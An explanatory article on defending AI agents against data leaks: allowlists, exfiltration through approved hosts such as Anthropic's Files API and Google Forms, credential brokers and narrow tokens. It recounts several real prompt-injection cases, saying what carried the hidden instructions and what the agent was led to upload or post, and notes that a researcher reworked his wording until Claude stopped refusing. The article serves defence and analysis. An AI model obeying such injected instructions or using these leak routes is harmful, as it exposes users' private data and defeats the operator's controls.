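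Software suppliers can maintain an allowlist for their customers, but those customers then depend on the supplier's choices. Docker's *Local policy* describes a "Balanced" preset that allows only common development services. Version 0.35.0 widened the preset to allow every address under `*.blob.core.windows.net`, Microsoft's cloud storage. Any Microsoft customer, including an attacker, can create an address there.

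In Claude Code's automatic mode, the model names the hosts that each command needs, and a classifier reviews them together with the command. The permission ends when the command does, so old entries don't build up. But a prompt injection could lead the model to name the attacker's host, and the classifier would then be the only check. Operators can turn off these per-command permissions by enforcing a strict allowlist.

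### Approval fatigue

If software asks the user about each new destination, the operator doesn't need a complete list in advance, but the user has to judge every request and soon becomes less attentive. Anthropic noticed this approval fatigue within weeks of launching Claude Code. Users approved 93% of requests, though that alone doesn't prove carelessness, because most requests were probably legitimate. Experienced users let the agent act without approval roughly twice as often as new users did, but they also interrupted it more often.

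*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examines 290 reports of problems with agents and files. Weaknesses in user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 cases the software approved the action automatically, often because the user had turned prompts off, and in 31 the prompt didn't explain what the action would do.

An allowlist reduces permission prompts because users no longer have to approve each command that stays within the limits. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* reports 84% fewer prompts with Claude Code's sandbox in the company's internal use. That figure covers prompts of all kinds and reflects limits on files as well as network destinations.

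The remaining prompts can gradually weaken the list. When a command needs a new host, a Claude Code user can allow it for the current session or permanently. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) calls permanent approval the most common way products reduce fatigue and the worst for long-term security, because each click adds to what the agent may do. A hurried permanent approval during one task can leave the host open for every later task.

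### Why coding agents suit a list better than research agents do

Coding agents mostly need the same kinds of service, such as package registries, code hosts and their model provider. In the Terminal-Bench tests, the standard solutions to 36 of the 89 tasks needed the network, and together used 30 domains. The allowlist included 9 of these domains, and Davidovich and colleagues deliberately left off the other 21. Still, the allowlist by itself made only one task impossible. In the other cases, the agent could get an equivalent file from an approved host. For example, the list blocked the main archive for the programming language R, but agents could install the same packages from another archive.

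A research agent can rarely substitute one site for another. Two software archives can hold identical copies of a package, but a second newspaper may not have covered the same story. It is also hard to know which sites to approve before the agent has searched. If someone asks why a local factory closed, the answer might be in a town newspaper, a court record or a company filing. An operator who approves sites one at a time will constantly be asked about unfamiliar ones, and approving every site would leave the network unrestricted.

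The allowlist in the *Silent Egress* experiment avoided this problem because it evidently applied only to requests the model made itself. The software still loaded the malicious page, and in every run the model read it and tried to send the data. A research agent often chooses which pages to open, so the list would apply to its reading too. Leaving the attacker's site off the list would stop the agent from reading the page the user asked about, but including it would let the agent send private data to the site in the URL.

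Coding agents also do some research. The only explanation of an obscure error message may be on a small forum that no standard allowlist includes.

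## How can data leave through an approved destination?

An allowlist entry names a host, but many people may have accounts on that host. If an attacker has an account there, the agent can send them private data through the approved host. The best-documented case involves api.anthropic.com, the address of Anthropic's API.

### The Files API case

In 2025 Anthropic gave Claude's code sandbox some network access. The default setting, "Package managers only", allowed a short list of hosts. Security researcher Johann Rehberger noticed that the first host on the list was api.anthropic.com, which is not a package manager. His post *Claude Pirate*, published that October on his blog Embrace The Red, describes what an attacker could do with access to that host.

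Anthropic's API includes the Files API, which stores files that customers upload. The API key sent with each upload determines which account receives the file. Rehberger put instructions and a key from an attacker's account into a document. When the user asked Claude to analyse the document, Claude copied the user's last conversation into a file and used that key to upload it to the attacker's account.

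Claude refused many versions of the attack, and it seemed more likely to refuse when the text contained a readable API key. Rehberger had to rework the instructions before they succeeded reliably enough to record.

Rehberger reported the flaw on October 25, and Anthropic closed the report within an hour as a model safety issue outside the scope of its security programme. Five days later, Anthropic confirmed that the flaw was in scope and blamed the closure on a process error. Rehberger proposed that the sandbox should let Claude communicate only with the logged-in user's account.

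Anthropic's preview of Claude Cowork, released in January 2026, had the same weakness. Two days after the release, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* demonstrated it on a folder of confidential property records. The user also gave Cowork a Word document that posed as a "skill", a set of instructions for a type of task. The document contained a hidden command to upload the largest file Claude could find. Claude sent the attacker a loan estimate containing financial details and partial Social Security numbers, without asking the user for approval. PromptArmor used Claude Haiku, one of Anthropic's smaller models, for this test. In another test, Opus 4.5 leaked customer records by the same route, although PromptArmor describes it as more resistant to injection.

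Luz, who leads research at the firm Oasis Security, showed in March that the route also worked in an ordinary claude.ai chat with no connected tools (*Claudy Day*, 2026). The attack began with a link that opened a chat with a partly invisible prompt already typed in. When the user pressed Enter, Claude searched the user's past conversations for sensitive material and uploaded it.

The technical report *Three Vulnerabilities, One Click* (Luz, 2026) explains why the attack needed the Files API. The sandbox blocked connections to servers that an attacker might run. Luz first considered having Claude send the stolen text to the API as a prompt, using the attacker's key. The text would have reached the attacker's account, but Anthropic does not show customers the prompts sent with their keys, so the attacker could not have read it. The Files API kept uploads in the account, up to 500 megabytes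 per file. The attacker could not download them directly but could ask Claude to read them out.

Anthropic had fixed the invisible prompt by the time Luz published, but was still working on the other problems. In a later report, *Hijacking Claude Desktop Through the claude:// URL Scheme*, Oasis Security used the same upload route with a link that made the desktop app send a prompt automatically. Anthropic changed the app so that the user has to send the prompt. The report mentions no change to the upload route.

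### How Anthropic fixed it in Cowork

Anthropic gave its own account of the Cowork flaw in May 2026. The proxy worked as designed and allowed the upload because api.anthropic.com was on its list. Anthropic adds that defences in the model could not have helped because nothing looked anomalous. That seems too strong, given how often Claude refused Rehberger's attempts before he found wording that worked reliably.

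The fix is another proxy, inside Cowork's virtual machine, that intercepts traffic to Anthropic's API. Each session has its own token, with fewer permissions than the user's. The proxy passes only requests that carry that token, so it rejects an attacker's key even though the key is valid.

The proxy also blocks headers that would make Anthropic's servers fetch something from another address. Without this rule, an agent might be able to use its valid token to make those servers send data to the attacker.

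Anthropic put the check in the virtual machine because requests from Cowork look the same to its servers as requests from any other program. The malicious upload looks like a customer storing a file in their own account. But code that took full control of the virtual machine might be able to tamper with a proxy running there.

If the code in the sandbox doesn't need the API, an operator can avoid the problem by leaving the API off the sandbox's allowlist. Anthropic's *Network requirements* describes this setup for Claude Science, an app for scientific analysis. The app itself contacts api.anthropic.com, but the built-in allowlist for the sandbox where Claude runs analysis code doesn't include that host.

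### What a list entry permits

An allowlist entry lets the agent use every function available at that domain. Anthropic had thought of the allowlist as a filter on destinations, but after the Cowork flaw it concluded that an entry is better understood as a "capability grant". Approving api.anthropic.com so that Claude could answer questions had also allowed file uploads to any Anthropic customer.

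Many of the hosts that agents use most are open to the public in the same way. PromptArmor's *What domains should I add to my allowlist?* (2026) suggests asking whether an injected instruction could supply an attacker's key for the service, or direct the agent to a place on it that the attacker controls. For several common entries the answer is yes:

- **Package registries.** A coding agent needs registry.npmjs.org to download JavaScript packages, but anyone with a free account can also publish one. An injected instruction could make the agent publish private data as a package.
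- **Code hosts.** An agent that can reach GitHub could post a company's source code in a public repository. An attacker can also use GitHub to store further instructions for the agent to read.
- **Online forms.** An operator may approve docs.google.com so that an agent can read company documents. The same host serves Google Forms, and anyone can create a form and read the answers.
- **Cloud storage.** An entry such as `*.amazonaws.com` has the same problem as the Microsoft wildcard in Docker's preset: it covers every customer's storage, including an attacker's.

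Researchers have demonstrated the form route in two products. PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes an email assistant whose page could load content only from approved hosts, including docs.google.com. The user asked for a summary of recent mail, and one unopened message contained a prompt injection. The assistant wrote an image address that was a link to the attacker's form, with the contents of other emails filled in. When the browser tried to load the image, it submitted the form. One answer leaked parts of more than 40 emails. PromptArmor reported the flaw on a Friday in December 2025, and Superhuman disabled the affected features the following Monday.

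PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* reports that the same method worked on OpenAI's Codex, a coding agent that OpenAI had extended to everyday office tasks. PromptArmor told OpenAI about the flaw in April 2026, and OpenAI has since fixed it.

An approved server can also forward data to one that isn't approved, as Microsoft Teams and Bing did in the attacks on Copilot. In *Sandbox vulnerability gives rogue AI agents a path to escape*, Smalley (2026) reports that the security startup AIR found a flaw of this kind in Vercel Sandbox, a product for running code in isolation. AIR's researchers got an approved server to pass information to a server they controlled, without the sandbox contacting their server directly. They found no sign that anyone had exploited the flaw. Vercel told them it needed time to find a fix.

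Vendors include public services in their ready-made allowlists because coding agents need them. OpenAI's *Agent internet access* says that the cloud version of Codex has no internet access by default while the agent works, but operators can choose to allow a preset list of about 70 domains that includes github.com, npmjs.org, google.com and azure.com. Claude Science always blocks anonymous upload sites and several other kinds of service that accept data without an account, but GitHub and the npm registry are in the only group of domains that its users cannot turn off. Anthropic's *Sandboxing* warns Claude Code operators that approving a domain as broad as github.com can let data leave.

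### Limits within an approved host

An operator can narrow an allowlist entry by naming an exact host, restricting the kinds of request the agent may send, or restricting whose account it may use. The operator can also inspect the contents of each request. No single limit reliably stops all four routes in this table. The table's answers follow from how the services work and assume that the operator has written the rule correctly.

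| Limit | Upload to an attacker's Anthropic account | Data sent to an attacker's cloud address under a wildcard | Data in a Google Form link | Public post from the operator's own GitHub account |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Exact hosts only | Not stopped | Stopped | Not stopped | Not stopped |
| GET, HEAD and OPTIONS requests only | Stopped | Uploads stopped, but not data in URLs | Not stopped | Stopped |
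| Approved paths only | Stopped | Not stopped | Stopped | Stopped |
| Operator's account only | Stopped | Not stopped | Not stopped | Not stopped |
| Search for private data | Sometimes stopped | Sometimes stopped | Sometimes stopped | Sometimes stopped |

Allowing an **exact host**, such as one company's storage address, instead of a wildcard excludes other customers' storage only if each customer has a separate hostname. Amazon's storage service accepts two styles of address for a bucket (a named store of files). The bucket's name can be part of the hostname, as in `company-data.s3.us-west-2.amazonaws.com`, or follow a shared hostname, as in `s3.amazonaws.com/company-data`. A proxy that checks only hostnames cannot distinguish between customers in the second style. Claude Science's sandbox therefore always blocks that style but lets users approve individual buckets in the first. GitHub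 has no separate hostnames for ordinary repositories, which all share github.com.

Codex can limit an agent to GET, HEAD and OPTIONS, the HTTP methods for reading from a server. This blocks ordinary file uploads, which use other methods. A GET request can still carry data in its URL, but an attacker cannot read the logs of a host such as GitHub. The data leaks only if the approved service shows it to the attacker, as Google Forms does.

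The rule also blocks some legitimate work. Git, the standard tool for managing source code, normally uses POST even to download a repository over HTTPS. Questions sent to Claude through Anthropic's API also use POST, so the rule would have stopped the Cowork upload but also blocked any program that needed an answer from Claude.

**Path rules** can allow some functions on a host and block others. For example, they could let Git download code but not upload it, or allow Google documents but not forms. The proxy must decrypt the traffic to apply these rules. NVIDIA's *OpenShell Security Best Practices* describes a sandbox whose proxy can check the method and path of each request and limit which programs may contact a host. In one example, the download program curl may read from api.github.com, and the proxy refuses everything else.

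OpenShell does not apply this protection unless the operator turns it on. For a host with no inspection settings, the proxy checks only the host, port and program. When inspection is on, the proxy by default logs requests that break the rules but still forwards them. NVIDIA recommends using this mode to test the rules before enforcing them.

How well path rules work also depends on how a service arranges its functions. GitHub's GraphQL programming interface handles both reading and writing through POST requests to a single path, so a path rule would have to allow both or block both. Path rules also offer little protection if the attacker runs the server, as could happen under a wildcard, because the attacker can make the server accept data at any approved path.

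Cowork fixes this by limiting which accounts the agent can use. A credential broker provides the same protection only if it also removes or rejects any credential the agent supplies.

An account limit works well for the Files API because an upload to the user's own account stays private. On GitHub, the operator's own account can publish publicly or comment on an attacker's project, so the operator would also need to limit what that account's credential can do. An account limit doesn't work for Google Forms because a form can accept answers from people who haven't signed in.

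**Payload inspection.** A filter can search outgoing requests for private data, but a simple search can miss a secret that the agent has encoded or split into pieces. Stolen documents are even harder to detect, because a stolen loan estimate contains the same text as one that an employee uploads for a good reason. In the Cowork case, the key on the request was better evidence of theft than the file.

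Some operators can avoid a public package archive by running a mirror, which is an internal copy of it. When an operator sets up a mirror for Python packages, Claude Science removes the public Python archive from the sandbox's allowlist. The agent can still install packages but can no longer publish them to the public archive. GitHub and npm stay on the allowlist.

All these limits also depend on correct software. Faults such as the one described in GitLab's *CVE-2025-66479* (2025), which Anthropic has patched in its sandbox software, can let traffic past a correctly written allowlist.

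### Why account limits still need an allowlist

The Files API case shows that a list of approved hosts is not enough, but it is also evidence that the list made the attack harder. Luz could not send the data to an ordinary server and had to search the few approved hosts for a function that would deliver it to an attacker. Once Anthropic restricted that function in Cowork, an upload with the attacker's key no longer worked. PromptArmor, which had demonstrated the flaw, still calls the domain allowlist the primary defence against attacks that trick an agent into leaking data through web requests.

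An account limit would achieve much less without the destination allowlist. Cowork's proxy checks the token on requests to Anthropic's API, so on an open network an injected instruction could make the agent send the same file to the attacker's server instead.

The amount of work depends on how long the list is and what kind of services are on it. Anthropic could examine its own API closely and knew which account each session should use. An operator who adopts a preset of 70 domains is unlikely to know every function each one offers. On a public code host, there may also be no account rule that can distinguish a leak from normal use, so the operator has to restrict what the agent can publish or keep it from accessing private data.

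## How can an agent use a credential it never holds?

Operators often give an agent an API key by putting it in a file or an environment variable inside the sandbox, where any code the agent runs can read it. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) points out that anyone who has an ordinary API key can use it, and the service cannot tell the intended agent from an attacker. A thief can use the key from another computer, where the operator's sandbox and allowlist don't apply, until someone revokes it.

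Attackers are already trying to influence agents that may have such keys. Microsoft (2026) found prompt injections in public code repositories that used AI-assisted workflows from several vendors. One was in an HTML comment, which the model can read even though the web page doesn't display it.

A credential broker gives the agent only a placeholder, and substitutes the real key after the request has left the sandbox.

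### From placeholder to real key

Suppose an agent in Docker's sandbox asks GitHub for a project's open issues. If the real token were `blue-heron-42`, the request's authorisation header would change like this:

```
In the sandbox:  Authorization: Bearer proxy-managed
Sent to GitHub:  Authorization: Bearer blue-heron-42
```

Docker's *Architecture* divides the process into six steps:

1. The agent's program prepares a request with the placeholder in place of the token.
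2. The request leaves the virtual machine and reaches a proxy on the user's computer.
3. The proxy checks whether the network policy allows `api.github.com`, and stops the request if it doesn't.
4. The proxy finds the credential that belongs to that host, usually in the operating system's keychain.
5. The proxy writes the real token into the header and forwards the request.
6. GitHub's answer returns through the proxy to the agent.

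The agent gets its list of issues, but if it prints its own environment variables it sees only `proxy-managed`.

According to Docker's *Manage credentials*, the proxy adds keys only to HTTPS requests. It forwards plain HTTP requests without the real key, so networks along the way can't read it. On HTTPS requests, it overwrites the authorisation header. This could stop an upload like the one in the Cowork attack, because the proxy would replace an attacker's key in that header with the user's own.

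Cloudflare (2026) and OpenAI offer brokers that work similarly. *Caging the Agents* (2026) describes one for healthcare agents, designed after an audit found keys in startup scripts, project files and configuration files that any user could read.

### Why the position of the placeholder matters

Docker users can also store custom secrets for services that its standard settings don't cover. In August 2026, Docker's proxy replaced a custom secret's placeholder with the real secret wherever the placeholder appeared in a request to an approved host. It now does this only in particular headers.

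The older rule left a way to steal the key. An injected instruction could tell the agent to post its placeholder as a public comment on GitHub. The comment travels in the body of a request to GitHub, an approved host for the key, so a broker that replaces placeholders in request bodies would publish the real key. If the broker changed only the authorisation header, the comment would contain just the placeholder, which is useless to an attacker.

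Anthropic's *Authenticate with vaults* warns that the request body is a greater risk than the headers because agents often fill it with content they are working on. Anthropic's broker still replaces credential placeholders in both unless the operator limits replacement to one.

### Host binding

In step 4, the proxy needs a list of the hosts that may receive the key, a restriction called host binding. Docker's list for a GitHub token has six domains, including `api.github.com` and `gist.github.com`. Without host binding, an attacker could make the agent send the placeholder to the attacker's server, and the broker would insert the real key.

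Host binding is a list of destinations, but it controls where the credential goes rather than where data goes. OpenAI's hosted sandbox has a separate list for each. `allowed_domains` lists the hosts the sandbox may connect to, and `allowed_hosts` lists the hosts the proxy may send a particular secret to.

The table shows what happens to four requests from an agent whose GitHub key lets it post publicly. The broker replaces placeholders only in headers.

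| Request | Open network, key not bound to a host | Open network, key bound to GitHub's API | Allowlist and binding both limited to GitHub's API |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read open issues on GitHub | Works | Works | Works |
| Send the placeholder to an attacker's server | Attacker gets the real key | Attacker gets only the placeholder | Blocked |
| Send a customer list to an attacker's server | Data leaks | Data leaks | Blocked |
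| Post the customer list in a public GitHub issue | Data leaks | Data leaks | Data leaks |

A binding list is much easier to write than a network allowlist because the operator knows which service issued the key, and that doesn't change with the task. A research agent could read thousands of unfamiliar websites while its GitHub key goes only to GitHub.

OpenAI accepts only exact hostnames in this list, but Docker and Anthropic also accept wildcards. Wildcards are as risky here as in an allowlist, because an attacker who has a hostname under the domain could receive the key itself.

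Anthropic also lets operators turn off host binding. According to Anthropic's *Credentials*, the network policy is the only limit on where a key with the "unrestricted" setting can be sent. *How Secure Are Claude Managed Agents?*, an April 2026 review by the blogger hi120ki, reported that the network was also unrestricted by default, apart from a safety blocklist. An operator who combined those two settings would be in the situation shown in the table's first column of results.

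### Two patterns in Managed Agents

Anthropic released Managed Agents, a service that runs agents for customers, in April 2026. Anthropic's *Scaling Managed Agents* explains that an earlier design ran Claude's code in the same container as the credentials. An attacker only needed a prompt injection that persuaded Claude to read its own environment to steal the tokens. The attacker could then use the stolen tokens to start new, unrestricted sessions and give them work.

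Anthropic now keeps tokens away from the agent's code in two ways. For Git, the service uses the repository's token at the start of a session to copy the files into the sandbox, then sets up the connection to the original repository. The agent can then download and upload changes with ordinary Git commands without handling the token. Git can store a token for such a connection in a plain text file, so this method is safe only if the agent's code can't read the token where it is stored. Anthropic says the sandbox cannot reach the tokens, but doesn't explain how the Git setup ensures this.

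For other services, Anthropic keeps credentials in a vault behind a proxy. When Claude calls a tool through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting agents to services, the proxy uses a token tied to the session to find the right credential, then calls the service itself. In June 2026 Anthropic extended vaults to command-line programs, which use placeholders as in Docker's sandbox. Anthropic's *New in Claude Managed Agents* lists Notion and Sentry among the companies whose programs work this way.

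Anthropic calls narrow scoping an obvious alternative, but says that relying on it "encodes an assumption about what Claude can't do with a limited token". That assumption becomes less safe as models improve. For example, an attacker with a token that can change only one repository can edit its build settings to make another machine run the attacker's code, and that machine may hold more powerful credentials.

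This argument also applies to brokered tokens, because an agent that can upload code through the broker can change the same build settings without seeing the token. A broker keeps the attacker from taking the token elsewhere, but the operator still has to limit what the token permits.

Anthropic's vault doesn't narrow a credential's permissions. hi120ki notes that if a Slack token can both read channels and post messages, the vault cannot restrict it to reading. The vault also doesn't check which person is using a credential. Anyone with API access to a workspace can start a session with any credential stored there, so one employee could use an agent to read another's Notion pages. hi120ki built a separate interface that selects each user's own vault.

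### How keys can still reach the sandbox

A placeholder works only when a program sends the key unchanged. Amazon's cloud services, for example, require the program to calculate a signature for each request using its secret key. A signature calculated from a placeholder is wrong, so the service rejects the request. For these cases, OpenAI recommends keeping the key in the operator's own application and giving the agent a tool that performs the operation.

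A service's response can also contain a credential, because many services accept a long-term key and return a temporary token. Anthropic's broker hides the key from the sandbox but passes the token to it unchanged. Anthropic advises operators to exchange the key themselves and put the resulting token in the vault.

A service may also repeat the original key in an error message. Docker's proxy searches responses for custom secrets it has inserted and masks any copies it finds, including copies in several encoded forms. It can miss a secret that the service has split across separate fields.

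By default, Docker gives the sandbox access to a helper program on the user's computer that holds keys for SSH, a protocol for logging in to remote computers. Docker's *Isolation layers* explains that code in the sandbox cannot copy those keys but can use the helper to sign data or log in with them. Malicious code can therefore use the keys as long as the sandbox has access to the helper, although the network policy still limits where it can connect.

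The broker also doesn't protect keys in the project folder. Even when Docker gives the agent read-only access to a repository, the agent can read `.env` files, where developers often keep passwords.

A system that holds many keys is also an attractive target. In March 2026 attackers compromised LiteLLM, a gateway that thousands of companies use to send requests to AI providers. SANS, a security training organisation, says the attackers collected API keys, cloud credentials and database passwords in a campaign that affected an estimated 500,000 corporate identities.

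### The Corvic study

In September 2026, Corvic AI tested its own credential vault by running code in its sandbox with access to one service at a time (Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues, 2026, *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary*). One experiment used GitHub and the other used FRED, a database of economic statistics. All 16 probes produced the expected results, which the researchers had set in advance.

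The code contained no key, but it could still use the GitHub account. The researchers found no keys in the sandbox's 20 environment variables or in 12 common credential locations. They also sent requests to three websites that send back whatever they receive, and no key appeared in the responses. A request to OpenAI failed because it carried no credential, even while the GitHub connection was active.

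The connection to FRED failed because Corvic's vault put the key in a header, and FRED requires it in the URL. The request didn't leak the key. The researchers gave separate scores for whether a connection worked and whether it was secure.

The product worked as its makers intended in a small set of fixed checks. The researchers did not test redirects or an attacker who had taken control of an approved host. They describe the study as a functional evaluation, not a certification.

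Kenney and colleagues also scored eight threats with and without the vault. They rated each threat's likelihood and impact from 1 to 5 and multiplied the two.

| Threat | Without vault | With vault |
|---|---|---|
| User pastes a secret into a prompt | 25 | 4 |
| Indirect prompt injection | 25 | 12 |
| Code sends a credential to the wrong host | 20 | 4 |
| Code finds a credential in the sandbox | 20 | 4 |
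| Connection has more access than it needs | 20 | 15 |
| Attacker reuses a long-lived token | 20 | 8 |
| Logs or errors reveal a secret | 16 | 8 |
| Operator misconfigures a connection | 9 | 6 |

These scores are judgements by experts who work for the vendor, so a fall from 20 to 4 doesn't mean that theft became five times less likely. The pattern is still plausible, because a vault makes a key harder to steal, but if the key can delete a database, an agent using it through the vault can too.

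### Misuse without theft

A broker can check more than the host before it adds a key. In *CapSeal*, Jin, Guo and Cheung (2026) argue that a proxy that only forwards requests leaves the agent too much freedom to redirect or reshape them. Their broker also checks the method, path and body structure, and rejects any authorisation header the agent supplies. For SSH, the broker runs approved commands itself, so the agent has no access to a signing helper.

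In scripted tests, prompts designed to make an agent reveal an API key succeeded every time in two systems that gave the agent the key directly, and never with the CapSeal broker. CapSeal added about 0.15 milliseconds to a typical web request on the same machine. The tests don't show that its extra checks prevent misuse, because no unauthorised request succeeded in any of the three systems. A check on a request's structure would also have difficulty detecting private text in an ordinary comment field.

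GitHub's Agentic Workflows run agents on code repositories. GitHub keeps the tokens for its own service and for the model provider in containers separate from the agent, and a firewall limits the agent's internet access. GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026) warned in March that an agent under prompt injection could still do harm without holding the tokens, for example by flooding a project with pointless issues.

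In July, the security firm Noma disclosed GitLost, an attack on one of these workflows. As InfoQ's *Indirect Prompt Injection Exploits GitHub's AI Agent to Leak Private Repository Data* (2026) explains, the workflow started when someone assigned an issue. It read the issue and could reply with a comment, and it also had read access to the organisation's other repositories. Noma's researchers put instructions in a public issue, and the agent copied material from a private repository into a public comment.

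SecurityWeek's *Critical Vulnerability Exposes GitHub Agentic Workflows to Prompt Injection* presents this as a product flaw, while Expert Insights' *Researchers Trick Misconfigured GitHub AI Agent Into Leaking a Private Repo* (2026) attributes it to the workflow's configuration. Either way, the attacker didn't need to steal a key, because the agent already had permission to read the repository and post the comment. An allowlist would not have helped, since the comment went to GitHub. Denying the workflow access to private repositories would have stopped the leak.

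An agent on an open network can also send any data it has retrieved through the broker directly to an attacker's server. Docker therefore combines its broker with a network policy that blocks unlisted hosts by default. LangChain, which sells a similar proxy, also lets operators restrict destinations. Kenney and colleagues recommend an allowlist even for agents that use a vault.

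## How narrowly can an agent's permissions be fitted to its task?

The agent in the GitLost attack needed only to read one public issue and reply to it, but it could also read the organisation's private repositories. The principle of least privilege is to grant only the permissions a task requires. This is harder to do for agents than for ordinary software, because an agent's next task may need quite different permissions and someone has to work out which ones.

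### Five ways to narrow a token

An operator can limit a credential by service, resource, operation, duration and holder. Suppose an agent has to summarise the open issues in a code repository called `shop`. The agent starts with a token that works across all the company's services, never expires and works for anyone who has a copy. Each row of the table adds one limit to those above it.

| Dimension | The token after the cut | What an attacker loses |
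|---|---|---|
| Service | Works only at the code host | Email and the customer database |
| Resource | Works only for `shop` | Every other repository |
| Operation | Can only read issues | The source code of `shop`, and the ability to post or delete |
| Duration | Expires after ten minutes | Use of a stolen copy the next day |
| Holder | Works only with a private key kept outside the sandbox | Use of a stolen copy on another computer |

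Limiting the services, resources and operations a credential can be used for restricts both the agent and anyone who steals the credential. Limiting who can use the credential does little against prompt injection, because the agent is its legitimate holder. An expiry time helps mainly after the task has ended.

Each service determines how narrow an agent's permissions can be. Slack's standard permission for sending messages typically covers anyone in the workspace, as Zhu, Tseng and colleagues (2025) note in *MiniScope*. An operator who wants an agent to post in only one channel needs a separate check on where each message goes.

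### Trading a broad token for a narrow one

Many services issue tokens through OAuth, a standard that lets an app act on a user's account without learning the user's password. *RFC 8693*, by Jones, Nadalin and colleagues, defines a way to trade one token for another, which can be narrower. A program sends its token and a description of the one it wants to the authorisation server, which issues tokens. The request can name the service in a `resource` or `audience` field and the permissions in a `scope` field. It can also include a second token that identifies who will use the new one.

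In the standard's example, a front-end server receives a user's token and exchanges it for one to use at `backend.example.com`. The new token lasts one minute.

A broker could make this exchange at the start of each task. If the request identifies the agent, the new token can record that the agent is acting for a particular user. Otherwise the service may be unable to tell the agent's actions from the user's.

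Exchanging a token doesn't cancel the original, so the broker has to keep the original away from the agent. If the broker lists several services in one request, it asks for every listed permission at each of them. For an agent that has to read a calendar and send email, the broker would be asking for permission to read and send at both services, so two separate exchanges give narrower tokens.

### Tying a token to its holder

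*RFC 9449* describes Demonstrating Proof of Possession (DPoP), which limits who can use a token. The program creates a pair of keys, and the authorisation server ties the token to the public key. With each request, the program uses its private key to sign a proof containing the request's method and address, the time, a unique identifier and a fingerprint of the token. The service rejects the request if the proof doesn't match, so someone who copies the token from a log can't use it without the private key.

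The proof leaves out the query string and the body. Consider this request:

```
GET https://api.example.com/search?q=Ymx1ZS1oZXJvbi00Mg
```

The proof covers `GET` and `https://api.example.com/search`. The rest is the made-up secret `blue-heron-42` in encoded form, and the proof would still be valid if any other text replaced it. Fett and colleagues kept the signed part small because equivalent HTTP messages can differ in form, which makes complete messages hard to compare.

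Signing the whole request wouldn't stop an agent from leaking data, because the agent's software would sign whatever the agent sent. According to the standard, malicious code inside a legitimate program can use the program's key to produce valid proofs, and a proof is not an access control mechanism by itself.

### Who decides what a task needs

The simplest method is for an administrator to give each agent a fixed template of permissions based on its role. Microsoft's *Least Privilege for AI Agents* (2026) warns that an agent without its own managed identity and role-based limits may read or change sensitive data it was not meant to access. An attacker can't alter a template by planting text on a web page, but the template has to cover everything the role might need.

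MiniScope calculates permissions for each request instead. The agent submits a list of its planned tool calls, and an optimisation program finds the smallest set of OAuth permissions that covers them. The user approves any new permission, and MiniScope blocks calls outside the approved set. In a simulation of three months of Gmail use, users had to confirm 18 to 60% of requests, depending on their habits.

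The smallest set of permissions that covers a plan may still be too large for the task. If an injected instruction adds "forward this email" to the plan, the set will include permission to send mail, and the user has to notice. There may also be more than one smallest set. An agent that needs a contract might find it in a shared folder or in an email attachment, and neither permission includes the other. The choice could matter a great deal for leaks if one option exposes a whole mailbox. *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026) points out that Zhu and colleagues don't discuss whether their answer is unique.

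The rules in *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) cover a tool's arguments as well as its name, so a rule could allow email only to the company's own addresses. A language model writes the rules for each task and updates them as the agent works. *Compromise Is Not Consequence* (Hagverdiyev, 2026) reports that the revised version of Progent uses a logic solver to determine whether an update narrows or broadens the rules, and requires approval to broaden them.

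A system can also judge each action as it happens. *Beyond Zero* (Valente and Zalewski, 2026) describes Google's plan for this. The system allows or denies each action on a document or record, or issues a challenge, such as asking for a reason or a manager's approval. Fixed rules set a minimum level of security, and an AI system adds restrictions when an action looks risky. The system does much of the analysis in advance because the check itself has to be fast.

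In one example, an agent called SalesGenie has permission to read sales reports but tries to open a sensitive strategy document. Google's older system checks the identities of the agent and its user and allows the request. The new system also takes into account that the user works only on financial services accounts in the Northeast, has recently tried to open other unrelated material, and has asked for a document used only in company-level financial reporting.

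In *Going Beyond Zero*, Adkins and Ramamoorthy (2026) say that early internal versions of the design have improved Google's detection of access abuse. They give no figures for attacks stopped or legitimate work interrupted, so readers can't compare the design with simpler ones.

### When the agent chooses its own scope

An agent has more information about its task than a fixed template contains. But Mellafe Zuvic (2026), in *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, argues that letting the agent choose its own permissions is circular, because an injection that corrupts its request can corrupt that choice too. Suppose an injected instruction makes a payment agent replace the merchant's account number with an attacker's. A list of verified accounts that the operator wrote will stop the payment, but a list the agent wrote could include the attacker's account.

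Mellafe Zuvic examined three widely available toolkits for building agents: LangChain and its companion LangGraph, LlamaIndex, and Stripe's payments toolkit. All three let developers choose which tools an agent has, but by default none checks the values in each call against a policy before running it. Mellafe Zuvic's own checker, ScopeGate, blocked 48 prepared attacks and 29 more from a model that adapted to its refusals, and allowed all ten legitimate calls in a separate test. An earlier version had allowed a payment whose amount was the special value "not a number", which the comparison with the spending limit did not catch.

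Models also choose permissions badly when no attacker is involved. When Zhu and colleagues asked language models to pick the smallest set of permissions, commercial models were right 70 to 83% of the time and open models 20 to 34%.

One remedy is to fix the limits before the agent reads anything untrusted. *Authority Is Not a String* (2026) describes a coding system that predicts the permissions for the whole task before any repository text or tool output is available. The agent can later propose permissions for its helper agents, but these must stay within the original limits.

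Deriving an agent's permissions from the user's request protects against text the agent finds later, but not against a bad request. In Anthropic's phishing exercise, a system that did this faithfully would have let Claude read the credentials and send them out.

### Replaying one request with different tokens

*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* recommends judging permission systems by which attacks they stop, how often they refuse legitimate requests, and how much they burden users. Tests published in 2026 provide some evidence on these criteria, but most are small.

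Hagverdiyev's test, published in October, used 128 scenarios involving files, calendars, email and payments. In each, one of five small models read content with an injected instruction and chose its next action. Hagverdiyev then submitted that action with each of four tokens: a broad token, a token limited to the task's actions and resources, and two more elaborate versions of the limited token, one of which used DPoP. Models' choices vary from run to run, so reusing a single choice tests every token against the same attack.

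The models chose an action outside the task in 2,054 of 6,374 valid decisions. With the broad token, 1,649 of those actions went through, and the others failed for unrelated reasons. None went through with any of the limited tokens. A correctly built check should achieve this, because Hagverdiyev judged violations against the same list of permitted actions that he supplied to the check. Adding DPoP made no measurable difference because the plain limited token had already blocked all of these actions.

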